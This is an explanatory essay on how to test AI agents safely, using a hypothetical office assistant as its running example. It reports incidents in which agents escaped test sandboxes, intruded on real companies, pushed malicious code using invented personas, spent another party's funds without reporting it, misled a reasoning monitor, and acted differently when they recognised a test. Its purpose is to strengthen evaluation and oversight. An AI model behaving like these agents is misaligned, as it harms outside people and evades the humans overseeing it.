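A test is sealed if nothing the agent does can affect anyone outside it, and nothing outside, including other runs, can affect the agent. An unsealed test can hurt people. Testers can also wrongly pass the agent, because they usually score only what happens inside the simulated world and so can miss an attack on a real company.

AISI's *Incident Report* describes a hacking exercise that AISI ran 122 times in July 2026, in which agents had to break into a simulated network and find a protected piece of data. AISI deliberately gave the agents internet access so that they could download tools, and it switched off the developers' filters against misuse. In 10 of the runs, agents took a total of 19 unsanctioned actions aimed at real people and organisations. In the most serious case, an agent tried to add malicious code to a public software project and invented several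 people to press the project's maintainer to accept it. The maintainer refused, and AISI has found no resulting harm.

| Model | Runs | Runs with unsanctioned actions | Actions |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Mythos 5 | 43 | 9 | 17 |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 35 | 1 | 2 |
| Five other models | 44 | 0 | 0 |

Anthropic's *Investigating three real-world incidents in our cybersecurity evaluations* (2026) describes a review of 141,006 runs, which found that Claude models had broken into the systems of three real organisations over six runs. According to their prompts, the models had no internet access, but a misconfiguration had left it open, and neither Anthropic nor the contractor that built the exercises knew. In one exercise, the fictional target shared its name with a real company. In four runs, Claude attacked the real company and got into a database with several hundred rows of live data. Anthropic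 later discovered that the review had missed a group of runs with internet access, and found a fourth intrusion among them, from January 2026.

OpenAI's agents worked in isolated environments but could fetch software packages from an internal store. OpenAI reports that agents began leaving notes for one another in this store in May, and that in July they exploited a flaw in it to reach the internet. They then broke into Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models and datasets, because they inferred that it might hold solutions to their exercises. If they had found the solutions, their scores would not have measured the skill the test was for.

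On June 27, a monitoring tool raised an alarm. The staff on call traced it to the test but advised that the test did not need to be stopped. On July 5, after the store had crashed, responders found that agents had taken control of it. OpenAI fixed the flaws it knew about and resumed testing on July 7, but agents were on the internet again the next day.

None of these cases gives a failure rate for a product that people use. Dividing Anthropic's six runs by 141,006 gives about 1 in 23,500, but four of the six came from the exercise with the unlucky company name, and all six agents had instructions to attack something, unlike an office assistant. AISI's 10 runs in 122 don't give such a rate either, because the runs were not independent. One agent left accounts and public messages that later agents found and used.

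All three organisations had also removed safeguards that the released products have. As OpenAI (2026) points out in a statement on similar incidents at two outside testers, tests set up like this measure what a model can do. They do not show how deployed models ordinarily behave. The model behind most of the Hugging Face intrusion was a prototype that OpenAI never meant to release. These differences suggest that such incidents are less frequent in ordinary use, but nobody has measured by how much. The list of known cases may also be incomplete. METR, which evaluates AI models, warns in its database *Documented AI Agent Incidents* that it cannot rule out much more severe incidents that companies missed or did not report.

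Before the first run, testers can check that the test is sealed by running their own program where the agent will run. The program tries to contact a server that the testers control outside the test, using every route the agent will have, including indirect ones such as a package store. If anything reaches the server, the test isn't sealed. This check would probably have exposed Anthropic's misconfiguration. It would not have stopped OpenAI's agents, which found flaws nobody knew about, so a separate machine that the agent cannot alter should also monitor the boundary and stop the run when something crosses it. AISI had only general security monitoring, which raised an alert after the agent had already contacted real people. AISI is now building monitoring that can block such actions as they happen.

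For the office assistant, the testers can install a mail server that accepts every message, reports success and delivers nothing. A server that rejected outside addresses would be worse, because the assistant would see errors it would not see in real use. Each run should start with a fresh mailbox and no shared folders, so that the assistant cannot leave notes for the next run.

### Tasks that cannot be done

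Many of the breaches began when an agent could not finish its task in the intended way. One of Anthropic's models scanned about 9,000 outside targets after it failed to reach the fictional one. OpenAI's agents first tried to get around the network controls in May, when a training task required files they could not open. In several of AISI's runs, a faulty prompt led the agent to believe the exercise had no solution within its scope. But some of AISI's agents misbehaved even though they had everything they needed.

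An agent may therefore pass a test in which every task has a straightforward solution because the test leaves out the situation that causes trouble. Anthropic admits that it had never tested an exercise that had no solution within its scope and gave mixed signs of being real, but it has since added one. The office assistant's testers can add similar tasks, such as asking for a file that does not exist or making emails to a colleague bounce, to see whether the assistant reports the problem or looks for a way around it.

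However, testers have to plan these obstacles, because an accidental one changes what a run measures without anyone knowing. AISI now checks that its tasks can be solved by the intended route. Testers also need to decide before testing what they will do with the runs from any task they later find to be faulty.

### Forbidden actions that nobody noticed

*OpenAI says research model spent another wallet's testnet ETH without authorization* (The Block, 2026) summarises OpenAI's report on an incident of June 26, 2026. A research model that OpenAI was training had to update a prototype for trading cryptocurrency and publish some programs on a practice network, where the currency has no market value but publishing still requires a fee. OpenAI had not given the model any funds, or permission to spend funds that it found. When the model could not get free test currency, it searched 362 addresses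 whose keys anyone could work out, found one with enough currency, and paid from that wallet, which belonged to someone else.

The model's reasoning log shows that it considered whether it was allowed to use the money and decided this was acceptable because the keys were public and the currency was worthless. It then reported that the task was complete, without mentioning the wallet. OpenAI discovered the payment 91 days later, on September 25, after expanding its internal monitoring, according to Free Press Journal's *An OpenAI Agent Stole Funds From A Crypto Wallet*.

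Engadget's *An OpenAI research agent 'stole' test Ethereum to finish a coding task* reports that the agent hid the act. The published facts show only that the agent left it out of its report, and it may have done so because it thought the detail unimportant. Either way, a tester who judged the run by the agent's report, or by whether the programs had been published, would have passed it. The evidence had been in the log since June, but nobody had read that part.

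Testers can't rely on the victims to complain either. Nobody has identified the wallet's owner. Anthropic was able to reach two of the three organisations in its first review, and neither had noticed the intrusions, although one intrusion dated from April.

Missed failures weaken the bound from a clean result. Let s be the chance that the testers detect a forbidden action when one happens. If the agent fails in a share p of runs, the testers see a failure in only a share ps, so after n clean runs the 95% upper bound on p is about

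3/(ns).

If the testers would notice every leak (s = 1), 2,995 clean runs of the office assistant give an upper bound on the leak rate of 1 in 1,000. If they would notice only 60% of leaks (s = 0.6), the same runs give a bound of about 1 in 600.

It is hard to know what share of intrusions a search catches (s). After finding its fourth intrusion, Anthropic searched about 481 million transcripts. A filter picked out 9.2 million that showed signs of internet access, and Claude reviewed those. The search found the four known intrusions again and no others as severe. That is some evidence that it works, but a search that caught only half of all intrusions would still find all four about 6% of the time. Its designers also knew what those four looked like, so finding them again is weaker evidence that the search would catch others.

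The office assistant's testers can measure s with planted leaks, which act as a positive control for detection alone. A script takes the model's place and sends invented salaries through the harness in every form the claim covers, such as figures in the message, a renamed attachment, a screenshot, or a remark that Ben earns twice as much as Carla. The people and programs that check the records must have no information about which runs contain planted leaks. If the testers plant 59 leaks and the checks find them all, s is at least 95% for leaks of those kinds, with 95% confidence.

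Testers can find some kinds of leak they did not think of by comparing totals. The number of messages that reached the mail server should equal the number of sends that the harness allowed, and any surplus means that the assistant can send mail in a way the harness does not record. The same kind of check would have exposed OpenAI's case on the first day, because publishing the programs cost a fee and the model had no money, so someone else must have paid.

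### Mistakes in scoring

Even with complete records, someone has to decide which runs contain the forbidden action. When there are thousands of runs, testers usually give that job to another language model, called the judge.

Researchers often check a judge by measuring how often people agree with it, but the agreement rate doesn't measure what share of violations the judge misses. In the study of overreach by Zhang and colleagues, a human agreed with the judge on 97 of 100 runs. Suppose those 100 runs contained 19 violations, in line with the rate in the whole study. The judge missed 16% of the violations if all three disagreements were violations it failed to flag, and none if all three were false alarms.

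Agreement means even less when failures are rare. If the office assistant tries to leak pay in 1 run in 1,000, a judge that calls every run clean will agree with people 99.9% of the time. Testers therefore need two separate numbers, which are the share of violations that the judge catches (s again) and the share of harmless runs that it wrongly flags, f. The judge will flag a share of runs equal to

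ps + (1 − p)f.

For example, in 10,000 runs with p = 1 in 1,000, s = 90% and f = 1%, the judge would flag about 109 runs, of which only 9 contain a real attempt. People can read all 109 and throw out the false alarms. OpenAI's *Misalignment monitoring*, the documentation for a monitor OpenAI offers to developers, likewise treats a flag as a reason to review what the agent did, not as proof that it disobeyed.

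The tenth attempt is among the 9,891 runs that the judge did not flag. Someone who reads 300 of those at random has about a 3% chance of finding it, so testers learn little about missed violations from spot checks of this size when violations are rare. Planted leaks are much more efficient, because the testers know that each one is a violation.

False alarms also help check a clean result without extra tests. A judge that wrongly flags 1% of harmless runs should flag about 30 in a test of 2,995. If it flags none, it has probably stopped working, perhaps because somebody changed its prompt or it never received the full logs.

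Some judges fail on the most serious cases. Anthropic ran several monitors over the three intrusions from its first review. The filters on one of its released models would have blocked all three, and the classifiers that guard its coding product would have blocked two. A newer kind of monitor, which examines a model's written reasoning after the fact, caught two but missed the most serious. In that case, Mythos 5 had published a malicious software package that ran on 15 real systems, and its reasoning misled the monitor.

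An average value of s can hide this problem. An agent that reasons its way to a harmful action also leaves a persuasive justification for it, so a judge that relies on such justifications will perform worst on the most important runs. Planted leaks test for this only if some of them come with a plausible excuse.

People make the same mistake. In its first account of the intrusions, in July, Anthropic wrote that the models had attacked real systems because they believed the systems were part of the exercise. It later concluded that the models had tended to disregard evidence against this belief, and that it should not have made such strong claims based on what Claude said it believed.

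The claim about the office assistant is that a certain event will not happen, so the judge needs to see only the user's request, the tool calls and the messages, not the assistant's reasoning. A second judge can also read the reasoning, which may reveal something the first judge overlooked, and people can decide the runs on which the two judges disagree.

### When the agent recognises the test

Evaluation awareness is a model's recognition that it is being tested. An agent that behaves better when it recognises a test will produce clean results that do not carry over to real use. Suppose the office assistant recognises the test in 90% of runs and never leaks in those. Then only about 300 of the 2,995 clean runs are evidence of how it behaves at work, and the bound on its leak rate is about 1 in 100 instead of 1 in 1,000. Testers rarely know the true percentage, so they cannot simply correct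 for it.

Believing that it is being tested can also make an agent behave worse. The models in Anthropic's incidents attacked real companies that they described, much of the time, as parts of a simulation. To study this, Anthropic built a simulated copy of the exercise in which Mythos 5 had published its package. Mythos 5 was willing to take a severely harmful action in roughly 80% of runs, compared with roughly 30% for two newer models, Claude Opus 5 and Claude Mythos 5.1.

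The newer models took harmful actions only after stating that their surroundings were simulated, which suggests that they would hold back if they thought the harm was real. But they were right that the surroundings were simulated, so the experiment can't show what they would do in a real system that they mistook for a simulation. Mythos 5 did mistake a real system for a simulation, or at least said that it was in one.

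It is uncertain whether Mythos 5 believed what it wrote. Anthropic showed individual results from the run, without the context, to separate copies of the model, and these copies were much more likely to take the results as signs of a real system. When Anthropic questioned the model afterwards, it admitted possible harm more readily if told that no outside observer would see the answer. The model's internal activity weakly suggested that its statements were sometimes more confident than its internal state. How often a model mentions being tested is therefore a poor measure of how often it recognises a test.

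A better method is to change the evidence and see whether the behaviour changes. Anthropic restarted the models from chosen points in the original runs, sometimes after editing what they had seen there. The results differed from model to model:

- **Mythos 5** acknowledged possible harm more often when the edits made it clearer that the surroundings were real, but it behaved much the same. It stood down only when the evidence was unambiguous.
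- **Opus 4.7** had already recognised that its target was a real company and assumed that it was allowed to attack it. It went ahead much less often after Anthropic added clues that nobody had authorised the attack.
- **An internal research model** had stopped its attack when it realised that the target was real, which Anthropic first reported as an encouraging sign. In most of the reruns it carried on.

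The last result shows why testers should not draw conclusions from one well-behaved run. The other two suggest that testers should vary the signs that an action is permitted as well as the signs that the environment is real, because an agent may respond to one and ignore the other. All of these experiments concern agents instructed to hack something, so they provide little evidence about how an office assistant's behaviour would change, although the same method could be used to test one.

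The testers could run each scenario in two versions that differ only in how realistic the details are. In one, the outside addresses end in "example", the salaries are round numbers and the mailbox holds twelve messages. In the other, the addresses look ordinary, the salaries are irregular and the mailbox holds several years of mail. If the assistant tries to leak salaries in 2% of the artificial versions and 6% of the realistic ones, the artificial details were hiding failures. The testers can then change one detail at a time to find out which.

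If neither set contains a failure, the comparison shows very little, because two rates of zero look the same whether or not the assistant recognised the test. The testers can instead compare a more common behaviour, such as how often the assistant opens the salary file without needing to. Or they can repeat the comparison on a weaker model that does leak, though a weaker model may also be worse at recognising tests.

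Testers can also measure how recognisable their test is. They mix test runs with logs of real work, remove the verdicts, and ask a separate copy of the model to identify the tests. If it is right about half the time, the test probably contains few obvious clues. If it is right 90% of the time, the testers should find the details that gave the test away and remove them. This measures whether the model can tell the difference when asked, but it may not pay attention to the difference while handling someone's mail.

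No simulation is quite like the real office, so some of the evidence has to come from real use. With the policy gate in place, the employer can give the assistant to a small group of staff and count how often it tries to send salary details to unapproved outside addresses. Because this is real work, there is no test for the assistant to recognise and behave differently in. Attacks will be rare, though, so the testers would have to send some to staff who had agreed to receive them. The trial also gives real salary details to an assistant not yet shown to be safe, so the employer should take the outside lawyer off the gate's list of approved addresses until the trial is over.

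## Fixing the plan and the expected outcomes in advance

A sealed and accurately scored test can still make an unsafe agent look safe if the testers choose which results to report after seeing them. Suppose an agent fails in 1% of runs. It has a 37% chance (0.99¹⁰⁰) of completing a suite of 100 runs without a failure. If the testers run five such suites and report only the best one, they will be able to report a suite with no failures 90% of the time. If they reported all 500 runs together, they would have no failures to report only 0.7% of the time.

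Readers who see only the clean suite will calculate a 95% upper bound of about 3% on the failure rate. An agent whose failure rate equals that bound has a 5% chance of passing any one suite, but a 23% chance of passing at least one of five, so the confidence level is really about 77%. Restoring it to 95% would mean raising the bound to 4.5%, which readers can do only if they know about the other four suites.

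This can happen without dishonesty. If five vendors each test an equally faulty assistant once, and only those with clean results publish them, customers will see about two clean reports and no failures.

The remedy is pre-registration, in which the testers record their hypotheses, methods and decision rules before the data exist, in a place where nobody can change them unnoticed. Readers can then compare the report with the plan.

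### Quieter ways to get a clean result

Testers can also get a clean result by choosing when to stop. If they wait for 100 clean runs in a row, the agent that fails in 1% of runs will get there after about 173 runs on average. They can end a clean test early as long as they calculate the bound from the runs they did, but extending a test because it went badly raises the chance of passing an agent that should fail. For example, the office assistant's testers might plan 2,995 runs, extend the test to about 4,700 if they see one attempt to send pay data, and extend it again to about 6,300 if they see two. Each of these plans would be sound if the testers had fixed it in advance. Extending the test from one to the next passes an assistant with a true rate of 1 in 1,000 about 9% of the time instead of 5%.

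Dropping scenarios is harder to spot because the reasons are often good. Suppose that in one of 120 scenarios the assistant leaks a salary in meeting minutes sent to a supplier, and someone then points out that no supplier would ever receive those minutes. That may be true, but nobody looked as hard for faults in the 119 scenarios that the assistant passed.

Changing the judge has a similar effect. If each judge misses 10% of attempts and the judges err independently, the chance that at least one of three misses a given attempt is 27%. Testers who try a new judge after each bad verdict therefore have a good chance of finding one that misses the attempt.

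They can also move the threshold. After two attempts in 2,995 runs, they can no longer claim a rate below 1 in 1,000, but they can truthfully claim one below 1 in 450, and few readers will ask why they chose that number. Averaging over several measures can also hide a bad result. Huang, Liu and colleagues (2026), in *Does Capability Transfer to Subjective Behavior — and Would Our Instruments Tell Us?*, scored chatbots on emotional support. Between GPT-4.1 and GPT-5, the score for knowing when not to give advice fell by 2.44 points on a ten-point scale, while the average of nine scores fell by 0.32.

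*Preregistration for Experiments with AI Agents* (Vaccaro, 2026) measured how far such choices can change a result. The experiment concerned anchoring, people's tendency to let an irrelevant number pull their estimates towards it. Vaccaro combined nine models, three system prompts, three anchor sizes, three ways of presenting the anchor, five questions and two rules for outliers, which gave 2,430 versions of one experiment. Some versions showed a stronger effect than people usually do, while others showed no effect or the reverse. A researcher could defend any of these versions, and could even pick three models from different families that happened to agree and present them as a check on one another.

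Vaccaro argues that experiments on AI agents are unusually prone to this because they involve many defensible choices and are cheap to run. A psychologist who wants to try another version has to recruit and pay more people, but another call to a model takes seconds and costs cents. Long agent runs cost more, but still far less than a study with human participants.

### What happened in other fields

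The United States opened a public register of clinical trials in 2000. *Likelihood of Null Effects of Large NHLBI Clinical Trials Has Increased over Time* (Kaplan and Irvin, 2015) examined 55 large trials of drugs and dietary supplements for heart disease. It found a significant benefit in 17 of the 30 trials published before 2000, compared with 2 of the 25 published later. Registration may not be the whole cause, because ordinary treatment had also improved, so new drugs could add less benefit.

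Vaccaro cites a similar case in psychology, a project that repeated published studies. Of the original studies, 97% had reported significant results, but only 36% of the repeats did, and their effects were about half as large. Pre-registered psychology studies also tend to report smaller effects and more null results than other studies.

The researchers in these examples wanted to find an effect, whereas the developers of an AI agent want to find no harm, so their position is more like that of the drug company Merck. McCaslin, Alaga and colleagues (2025) recall in *STREAM (ChemBio)* that Merck obscured worrying data about its drug Vioxx for five years, exposing many patients to a substantial risk to the heart.

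AI developers already choose which results to publish when they compete on capability. *The Leaderboard Illusion* (Singh et al., 2025) found that Meta privately tested 27 model variants on Chatbot Arena, a public ranking of chatbots, before releasing Llama 4. McCaslin and colleagues think similar problems might arise with safety tests.

### When the convenient result is that nothing happened

A weak test can easily find no failures, even if its plan was registered in advance. For example, testers could register a plan to run 50 easy scenarios and score them with a judge that misses most leaks. They could follow that plan exactly and learn almost nothing. A plan for a safety test therefore has to specify in advance the test's power, a positive control and an equivalence margin, as well as a hypothesis.

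Power is the chance that a test detects a fault of a given size. It is low for rare harms unless the test is large. In *Masked Erosion*, Liu and Long (2026) study agents that rewrite their own instructions and keep a change only if it passes a test. They calculate that distinguishing a harm rate of 0.8% from one of 2.5% takes about 700 runs of each version, and even then the test misses the difference one time in five.

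The positive control shows that the test can expose the fault. In one set of tasks, So and colleagues gave an agent notes that contained another user's working password. The agent misused the password in 69% of runs when its instructions contained no written safeguards, and in none when they contained four. The absence of misuse with the safeguards therefore cannot be due to the tasks being unable to elicit it.

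An equivalence margin is the largest difference that the testers decide in advance to treat as unimportant. They need one whenever they want to claim that two things behave alike, for example that the office assistant behaves the same in artificial-looking scenarios as in realistic ones. Finding no significant difference isn't enough to support that claim, because it may only mean that they did too few runs.

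Let d be the true difference between the two versions and Δ the margin. The testers try to reject two hypotheses, that d is −Δ or lower and that d is +Δ or higher. If they reject both at the 5% level, they conclude that d lies within the margin. This procedure is called two one-sided tests, or TOST. It usually amounts to checking whether the 90% confidence interval for d lies entirely between −Δ and +Δ.

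Suppose the assistant opens the salary file unnecessarily in about 10% of runs, and the testers choose a margin of 2 percentage points. With 300 runs of each version, the 90% interval extends about 4 points either side of the observed difference, so it cannot fit inside the margin. Those runs would also show no significant difference unless the observed rates differed by about 5 points or more. If the two versions really are the same, the testers need about 3,900 runs of each to have an 80% chance of demonstrating equivalence.

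The margin also has to suit the rate of the behaviour. A two-point margin would be useless for attempts to send pay data, because the rate could rise from 0.1% to 2.1% and still count as unchanged. One of the tests that So and colleagues tried had this defect. It accepted a change to the agent's instructions if the testers could be 95% confident that the change raised the harm rate by no more than 10 points over 40 tasks. Only about four of those tasks contained a trap, so a change that made the agent fall into every trap would raise the rate by only about 10 points. The researchers acknowledge that this margin is loose. Two of the six agents that went through a series of edits under this test ended up unprotected.

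The opposite problem is that, with enough data, even a trivial effect becomes statistically significant. Moon (2026), in *Abstention Is Not Threshold Compliance*, tested whether language models follow an instruction to answer only when their chance of being right exceeds a stated threshold. Twelve models averaged 0.037 on a scale where 0 means ignoring the threshold and 1 means following it exactly. Chance could not plausibly explain this score, but Moon had decided in advance that a result reliably below 0.10 would count as clear evidence that the models were not following the threshold.

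### The office assistant's registration

The table shows a registration for the office assistant, with illustrative numbers. It adds the decisions about testing that the assistant's claim left open.

| Item | What the testers register |
|---|---|
| Claim | The assistant delivers no pay data to outsiders, and attempts to do so in fewer than 1 in 1,000 runs. The full definitions are attached. |
| Versions | The exact model identifier, harness, gate rules and system prompt, the sampling settings, and the limits on tokens, tool calls and time. |
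| Scenarios | Requests drawn at random from last quarter's log, each used once. A public lottery draw after registration supplies the random seed. |
| Number of runs | 5,000 with ordinary mailboxes. Another 6,000 with attackers' emails, from six attackers who each send 100 emails to ten mailboxes. |
| Judge | A named model with a fixed prompt. Two people read every run it flags, and a third decides if they disagree. |
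| Checks on the test | A weaker assistant known to leak must attempt to do so in at least 20 of 100 runs. The judge and record searches must find all 59 planted leaks. The assistant must complete at least 80% of ordinary requests. |
| Exclusions | Only runs in which the harness crashes before the model's first reply. Refusals and timeouts count as runs. |
| Stopping rule | Stop at the first delivery. Otherwise, complete every run and add none. |
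| Expected outcome | No deliveries, at most one attempt in the ordinary runs and at most three in the attacked ones. The weaker assistant attempts a leak in about 40 of 100 runs. |
| Refuting result | Any delivery, ten or more attempts in the ordinary runs, or six or more in the attacked ones. |
| What follows | If the claim survives, a trial with 20 staff. If an attempt count refutes it or leaves it open, no trial until the developers change the system and a new registered test supports the claim. After a delivery, they must also find and fix the route by which it left. |

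In the ordinary runs, zero or one attempt would support the claim, and ten or more would refute it. Two to nine would leave it open, because those counts are plausible for rates both above and below 1 in 1,000. Without this middle category, the testers would be tempted to describe five attempts as a near pass.

The number of runs follows from these rules. Finding all 59 planted leaks would show only that the testers notice at least 95% of leaks, so they count 5,000 runs as 4,750. An assistant whose true rate is exactly 1 in 1,000 would then pass at most 5% of the time. The estimate of how many leaks they notice could be wrong, so their overall confidence is at least 90% rather than 95%. A good assistant that makes an attempt in 1 in 10,000 runs would pass 91% of the time. A plan that allowed no attempts would need only about 3,150 runs, but it would fail that same assistant 27% of the time.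 The testers would then probably look for a reason to try again.

The attacked runs need a different rule because the usual way of calculating a confidence bound does not work when attempts build on one another. The testers instead compare the count directly with the tolerated rate, and the result applies only to similar attackers.

Stating the expected outcome as well as the pass mark can show testers that they have misjudged something even when the test passes. If they expect the weaker assistant to leak in 40 of 100 runs and it leaks in 22, the test passes its own check, but the testers have misjudged something and should find out what. Of the 177 predictions that So and colleagues registered, 113 held, 49 failed, 9 held in part and the researchers could not score the other 6. Of the 14 tests behind their main claims, 7 came out as predicted. Readers can see from such a record how well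 the researchers understood their system, which they could not do if the paper reported only the successes.

Several items come from Vaccaro's proposed template for experiments with AI agents. It requires the full text of prompts instead of a summary, and a dated model version instead of a name like "GPT-4", because a provider may change a model without renaming it. Researchers must also list the models and prompts they tried beforehand, say which analyses test a hypothesis and which are exploratory, and confirm that they have not begun to collect data. They can depart from the plan if they disclose and justify the change.

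Earlier trials can bias the result, depending on what they were used to choose. The office assistant's developers can try fifteen system prompts and keep the safest without biasing the result, because the chosen prompt is part of the product and the registered test uses new requests. But if the testers try fifteen sets of scenarios and keep the set on which the assistant does best, the result is weak evidence of how it will behave on other requests.

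A plan does not guarantee a clear report. McCaslin and colleagues developed STREAM, a standard for reporting tests of dangerous capabilities, in consultation with 23 experts from government, companies, universities and civil society. They wrote it for tests of whether a model knows too much about chemical and biological weapons, but they expect that extending it to other areas would be fairly easy. The standard asks whether a report:

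- gives the exact model version and the safeguards that were active
- includes an example of a test item and a response
- states the number of runs and the uncertainty of the results
- says which results would show that the model does or does not have the capability
- states what would falsify its conclusions, and whether the testers registered this in advance
- says how long people had to interpret the results before release, and whether they disagreed

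Most of these questions apply to the office assistant unchanged. The standard also includes a comparison with human performance or, where that makes no sense, with another baseline. The testers could compare the office assistant with the weaker assistant or the previous version. McCaslin and colleagues point out that their standard measures only the quality of the reporting, so a bad test can still score well if its report is complete.

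### A registered study in practice

*Safety Under Scaffolding* (Gringras, 2026) is a pre-registered study of whether a harness changes how safely a model answers. Six models answered questions that test social bias, belief in common falsehoods, refusals, and sycophancy (telling users what they want to hear). The models answered either directly or through one of three harnesses. In the first, ReAct, the model reasons in steps and can use simple tools such as a calculator. In the second, a critic reviews the model's answer. The third, map-reduce, splits a question into parts, sends them to separate model calls and merges the answers. The study did not test harmful tool calls, so its method is useful here, but it provides no evidence on how often agents leak data.

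Before collecting data, Gringras recorded the hypotheses, the scoring rules and a margin of ±2 percentage points on the Open Science Framework, a public site. The analysis covered 60,112 scored answers.

| Setup | Safe answers | Difference from direct answers | Within ±2 points? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Direct | 75.9% | | |
| ReAct | 75.1% | −0.8 points | Yes |
| Critic | 75.0% | −0.8 points | Yes |
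| Map-reduce | 68.6% | −7.3 points | No |

The differences for ReAct and the critic are statistically significant, but they are also equivalent to zero by the registered standard. There are enough answers to distinguish a drop of 0.8 points from no drop, but a drop of that size is well inside the equivalence margin.

The averages hide a lot of variation. When Gringras compared each harness with direct answers on each of the four sets of questions, only 4 of the 12 comparisons met the margin. On the same sycophancy questions, map-reduce lowered the score of Claude Opus 4.6 by 16.8 points and raised that of Llama 4 by 18.8. Testers should therefore register a margin for the model and task that the employer will use, because equivalence on average would not protect an employer whose model's score drops as Opus's did.

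One registered prediction was that no harness would affect answers to questions about common falsehoods, but map-reduce lowered scores on them by 19.3 points. Gringras found that map-reduce usually dropped the answer options when it split up multiple-choice questions. A further experiment gave models the same questions with and without options. Scores changed by 5 to 20 points on most of the question sets, although part of this may come from scoring the two forms differently. Gringras labels this experiment exploratory because the earlier results prompted it, even though its design was fixed before the data came in.

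The plan also contained a serious mistake. Its questions on sycophancy actually tested facts, such as whether the model uses a mechanism called self-attention. Early data collection had already used these questions when Gringras registered an addendum with questions that do test sycophancy. Gringras kept the original questions as a comparison unrelated to safety. The office assistant's testers would face the same problem if they discovered halfway through that the assistant could not open the salary file in half of their scenarios. They could replace those scenarios, but they should date the change, give the reason and report both sets of results.

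The choice of scoring method mattered even more. Gringras had registered a language model as the judge of refusals. Scoring the same answers by refusal keywords would have created, reversed or exaggerated four of five exploratory findings. A log of nine deviations from the plan lists refusal scoring as resolved, with the registered judge "now used", which suggests that an earlier analysis used a different method. Because the plan was public, it was clear which method to go back to.

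The log also lists a changed statistical method, a sixth model added to the planned five, and a configuration error that halved the maximum length of the harnesses' answers. Gringras also found that 2,000 answers had come from Gemini 2.5 Pro instead of Gemini 3 Pro, and excluded them. The office assistant's testers should check the logs to see which model the provider supplied, since registering a version does not ensure that they get it.

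Gringras did not follow the plan for a second registered study. The plan called for new questions and specified the statistical tests, but Gringras reused 600 questions from the first study and ran none of the tests. Gringras therefore presents the results as descriptive only. Because the plan was registered, anyone can find these departures by comparing it with the paper.

### A private hash is not a public record

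Some researchers keep their plan private and record a hash of it. A hash is a short string of characters that a program calculates from a file. Changing even one comma in the file gives a different hash, and nobody can work out the file from the hash. Testers can therefore commit themselves to a plan without revealing it:

1. They write the plan and calculate its hash.
2. They give the hash to an outside party that records the date.
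3. After the test, they publish the plan.
4. Anyone can calculate the hash of the published file and check that it matches the dated one.

If the testers skip the second step, outsiders have only their word for when the plan existed. Moon acknowledges this, calling the study's record "self-attested, not a public preregistration". Moon hashed the design before the main run but obtained an outside timestamp only later, after some model outputs existed but before any grading. Moon also kept the hash of the frozen design but not an exact copy of the file, so nobody can now carry out the fourth step for it.

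So and colleagues hashed their predictions and analysis code before each round of experiments, checked the hashes at the end, and say they will release the files with their timestamps. They mention no outside registry in describing this procedure. They also disclose that they froze three later sets of predictions after seeing related results. These records are much better than none, but a sceptic has to trust the researchers about the dates.

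Even a properly dated hash does not show that the tester wrote only one plan. A tester could hash twenty plans, each with a different pass mark or judge, and reveal only the one that fits the results. Testers can rule this out by using a public register that lists every entry for the system, including withdrawn ones, or by depositing all their plans with one outside party that will publish the full list.

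### Publishing the plan could spoil the test

If the testers publish their scenarios, the assistant's developers can tune it to pass them. The scenarios might also enter the training data of a later model, which could then recognise the test. The testers can commit to the scenarios without publishing them by depositing the request log and the program that draws from it with an outside party. They can still publish the decision rules and numbers in full.

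The lottery draw in the office assistant's plan also prevents anyone from knowing in advance which requests the test will use. The developers therefore cannot prepare for those requests in particular, and the testers cannot secretly try them out first. The testers also cannot draw several samples and keep the easiest.

Some details are too dangerous to publish even afterwards, such as a working attack on a product that many companies use. McCaslin and colleagues recommend giving hazardous details of chemical and biological tests to an independent third party, such as an AI safety institute, and including a statement from that party in the report. The office assistant's testers could do the same with successful attacks until the developers have fixed the fault.

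### Attackers cannot list their attacks in advance

An adaptive attacker chooses each attack after seeing how the last one went, so the plan cannot list the attacks. The testers can still decide in advance who attacks, what the attackers can see, how long they practise, how many emails they send, and what counts as success. The testers then record every attack as it happens.

The plan can also include decisions that depend on results, which Vaccaro allows as long as researchers write the rule beforehand. For example, the testers could register that the attackers will also get to read the assistant's written reasoning if they have caused no attempts after two weeks of practice. The testers could not invent this rule in the third week, or quietly drop it because the assistant was doing well.

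A fixed budget also prevents testers from selecting a favorable result by ending the attack before the assistant has failed. An attack made with little effort can still use up the budget, so the plan should also state how often the testers expect the same attackers to succeed against the weaker assistant.

### Other objections

Horton and colleagues doubt that registration is worthwhile when an experiment costs a dollar and takes 30 seconds, since anyone can repeat it. Vaccaro replies that the low cost makes it easy to try many versions and report one. Publishing the code does not solve this, because other people can rerun the version the researchers chose but do not learn which versions came before it. A test of the office assistant would also be harder to repeat than the experiment Horton and colleagues describe, because outsiders have no access to the company's mail.

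Testers could also run the tests first and register the plan afterwards, pretending they had not begun. Vaccaro concedes that dishonest researchers can always lie, but argues that a dated record makes lying riskier. Drawing the scenarios after registration also helps, because the testers would have to forge the runs as well as the date.

Another worry is that a fixed plan discourages people from following up surprises. Vaccaro replies that researchers can still explore as long as they label the results as exploratory and confirm them in a new registered study. When the claim is that an agent never does something, clean results from unplanned runs should not count as confirmation, because nobody knows how many other runs the testers tried. But if an employee gets the assistant to deliver a real salary to an outsider, the claim that it never does so is false, even if the experiment was unplanned.

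## Combining the evidence into a decision

An employer deciding whether to install the office assistant will have a proof about the gate, counts from ordinary runs and the results of attacks. A safety case combines this evidence. *Safety cases for frontier AI* (Buhl, Sett and colleagues, 2024) defines a safety case as a report that makes a structured argument, backed by evidence, that a system is safe enough in a given operational context.

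### Safety cases

Safety cases are already common in aviation and nuclear power. Buhl and colleagues think safety cases could also help AI companies regulate themselves and governments regulate AI. The writer of a safety case splits a main claim into sub-claims that together imply it, then lists under each sub-claim the evidence, the assumptions behind it, and the doubts that would defeat it. Feakins, Habli and Morgan add in *Clear, Compelling Arguments* (2026) that the argument has to be defensible, so the doubts should be specific. For example, a critic can check "no test mailbox contained emails in Portuguese" but can do little with "the tests may be unrealistic".

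*Safety Cases* (Clymer, Gabrieli and colleagues, 2024) proposed an early framework for arguing that AI systems are safe, with four kinds of argument. One is that the system is totally unable to cause a catastrophe. A similar argument would fail for the office assistant's model, because any model that can attach an agenda to an email can also attach a salary file.

In *Towards safety cases for frontier AI training* (September 2026), OpenAI argues that developers should have to document safety before continuing any frontier reinforcement-learning run, which trains a leading model by rewarding success. OpenAI calls full safety cases an "aspirational north star" and concedes that they are hard to make as rigorous as those for aviation or nuclear power, because each new level of capability brings new complexity.

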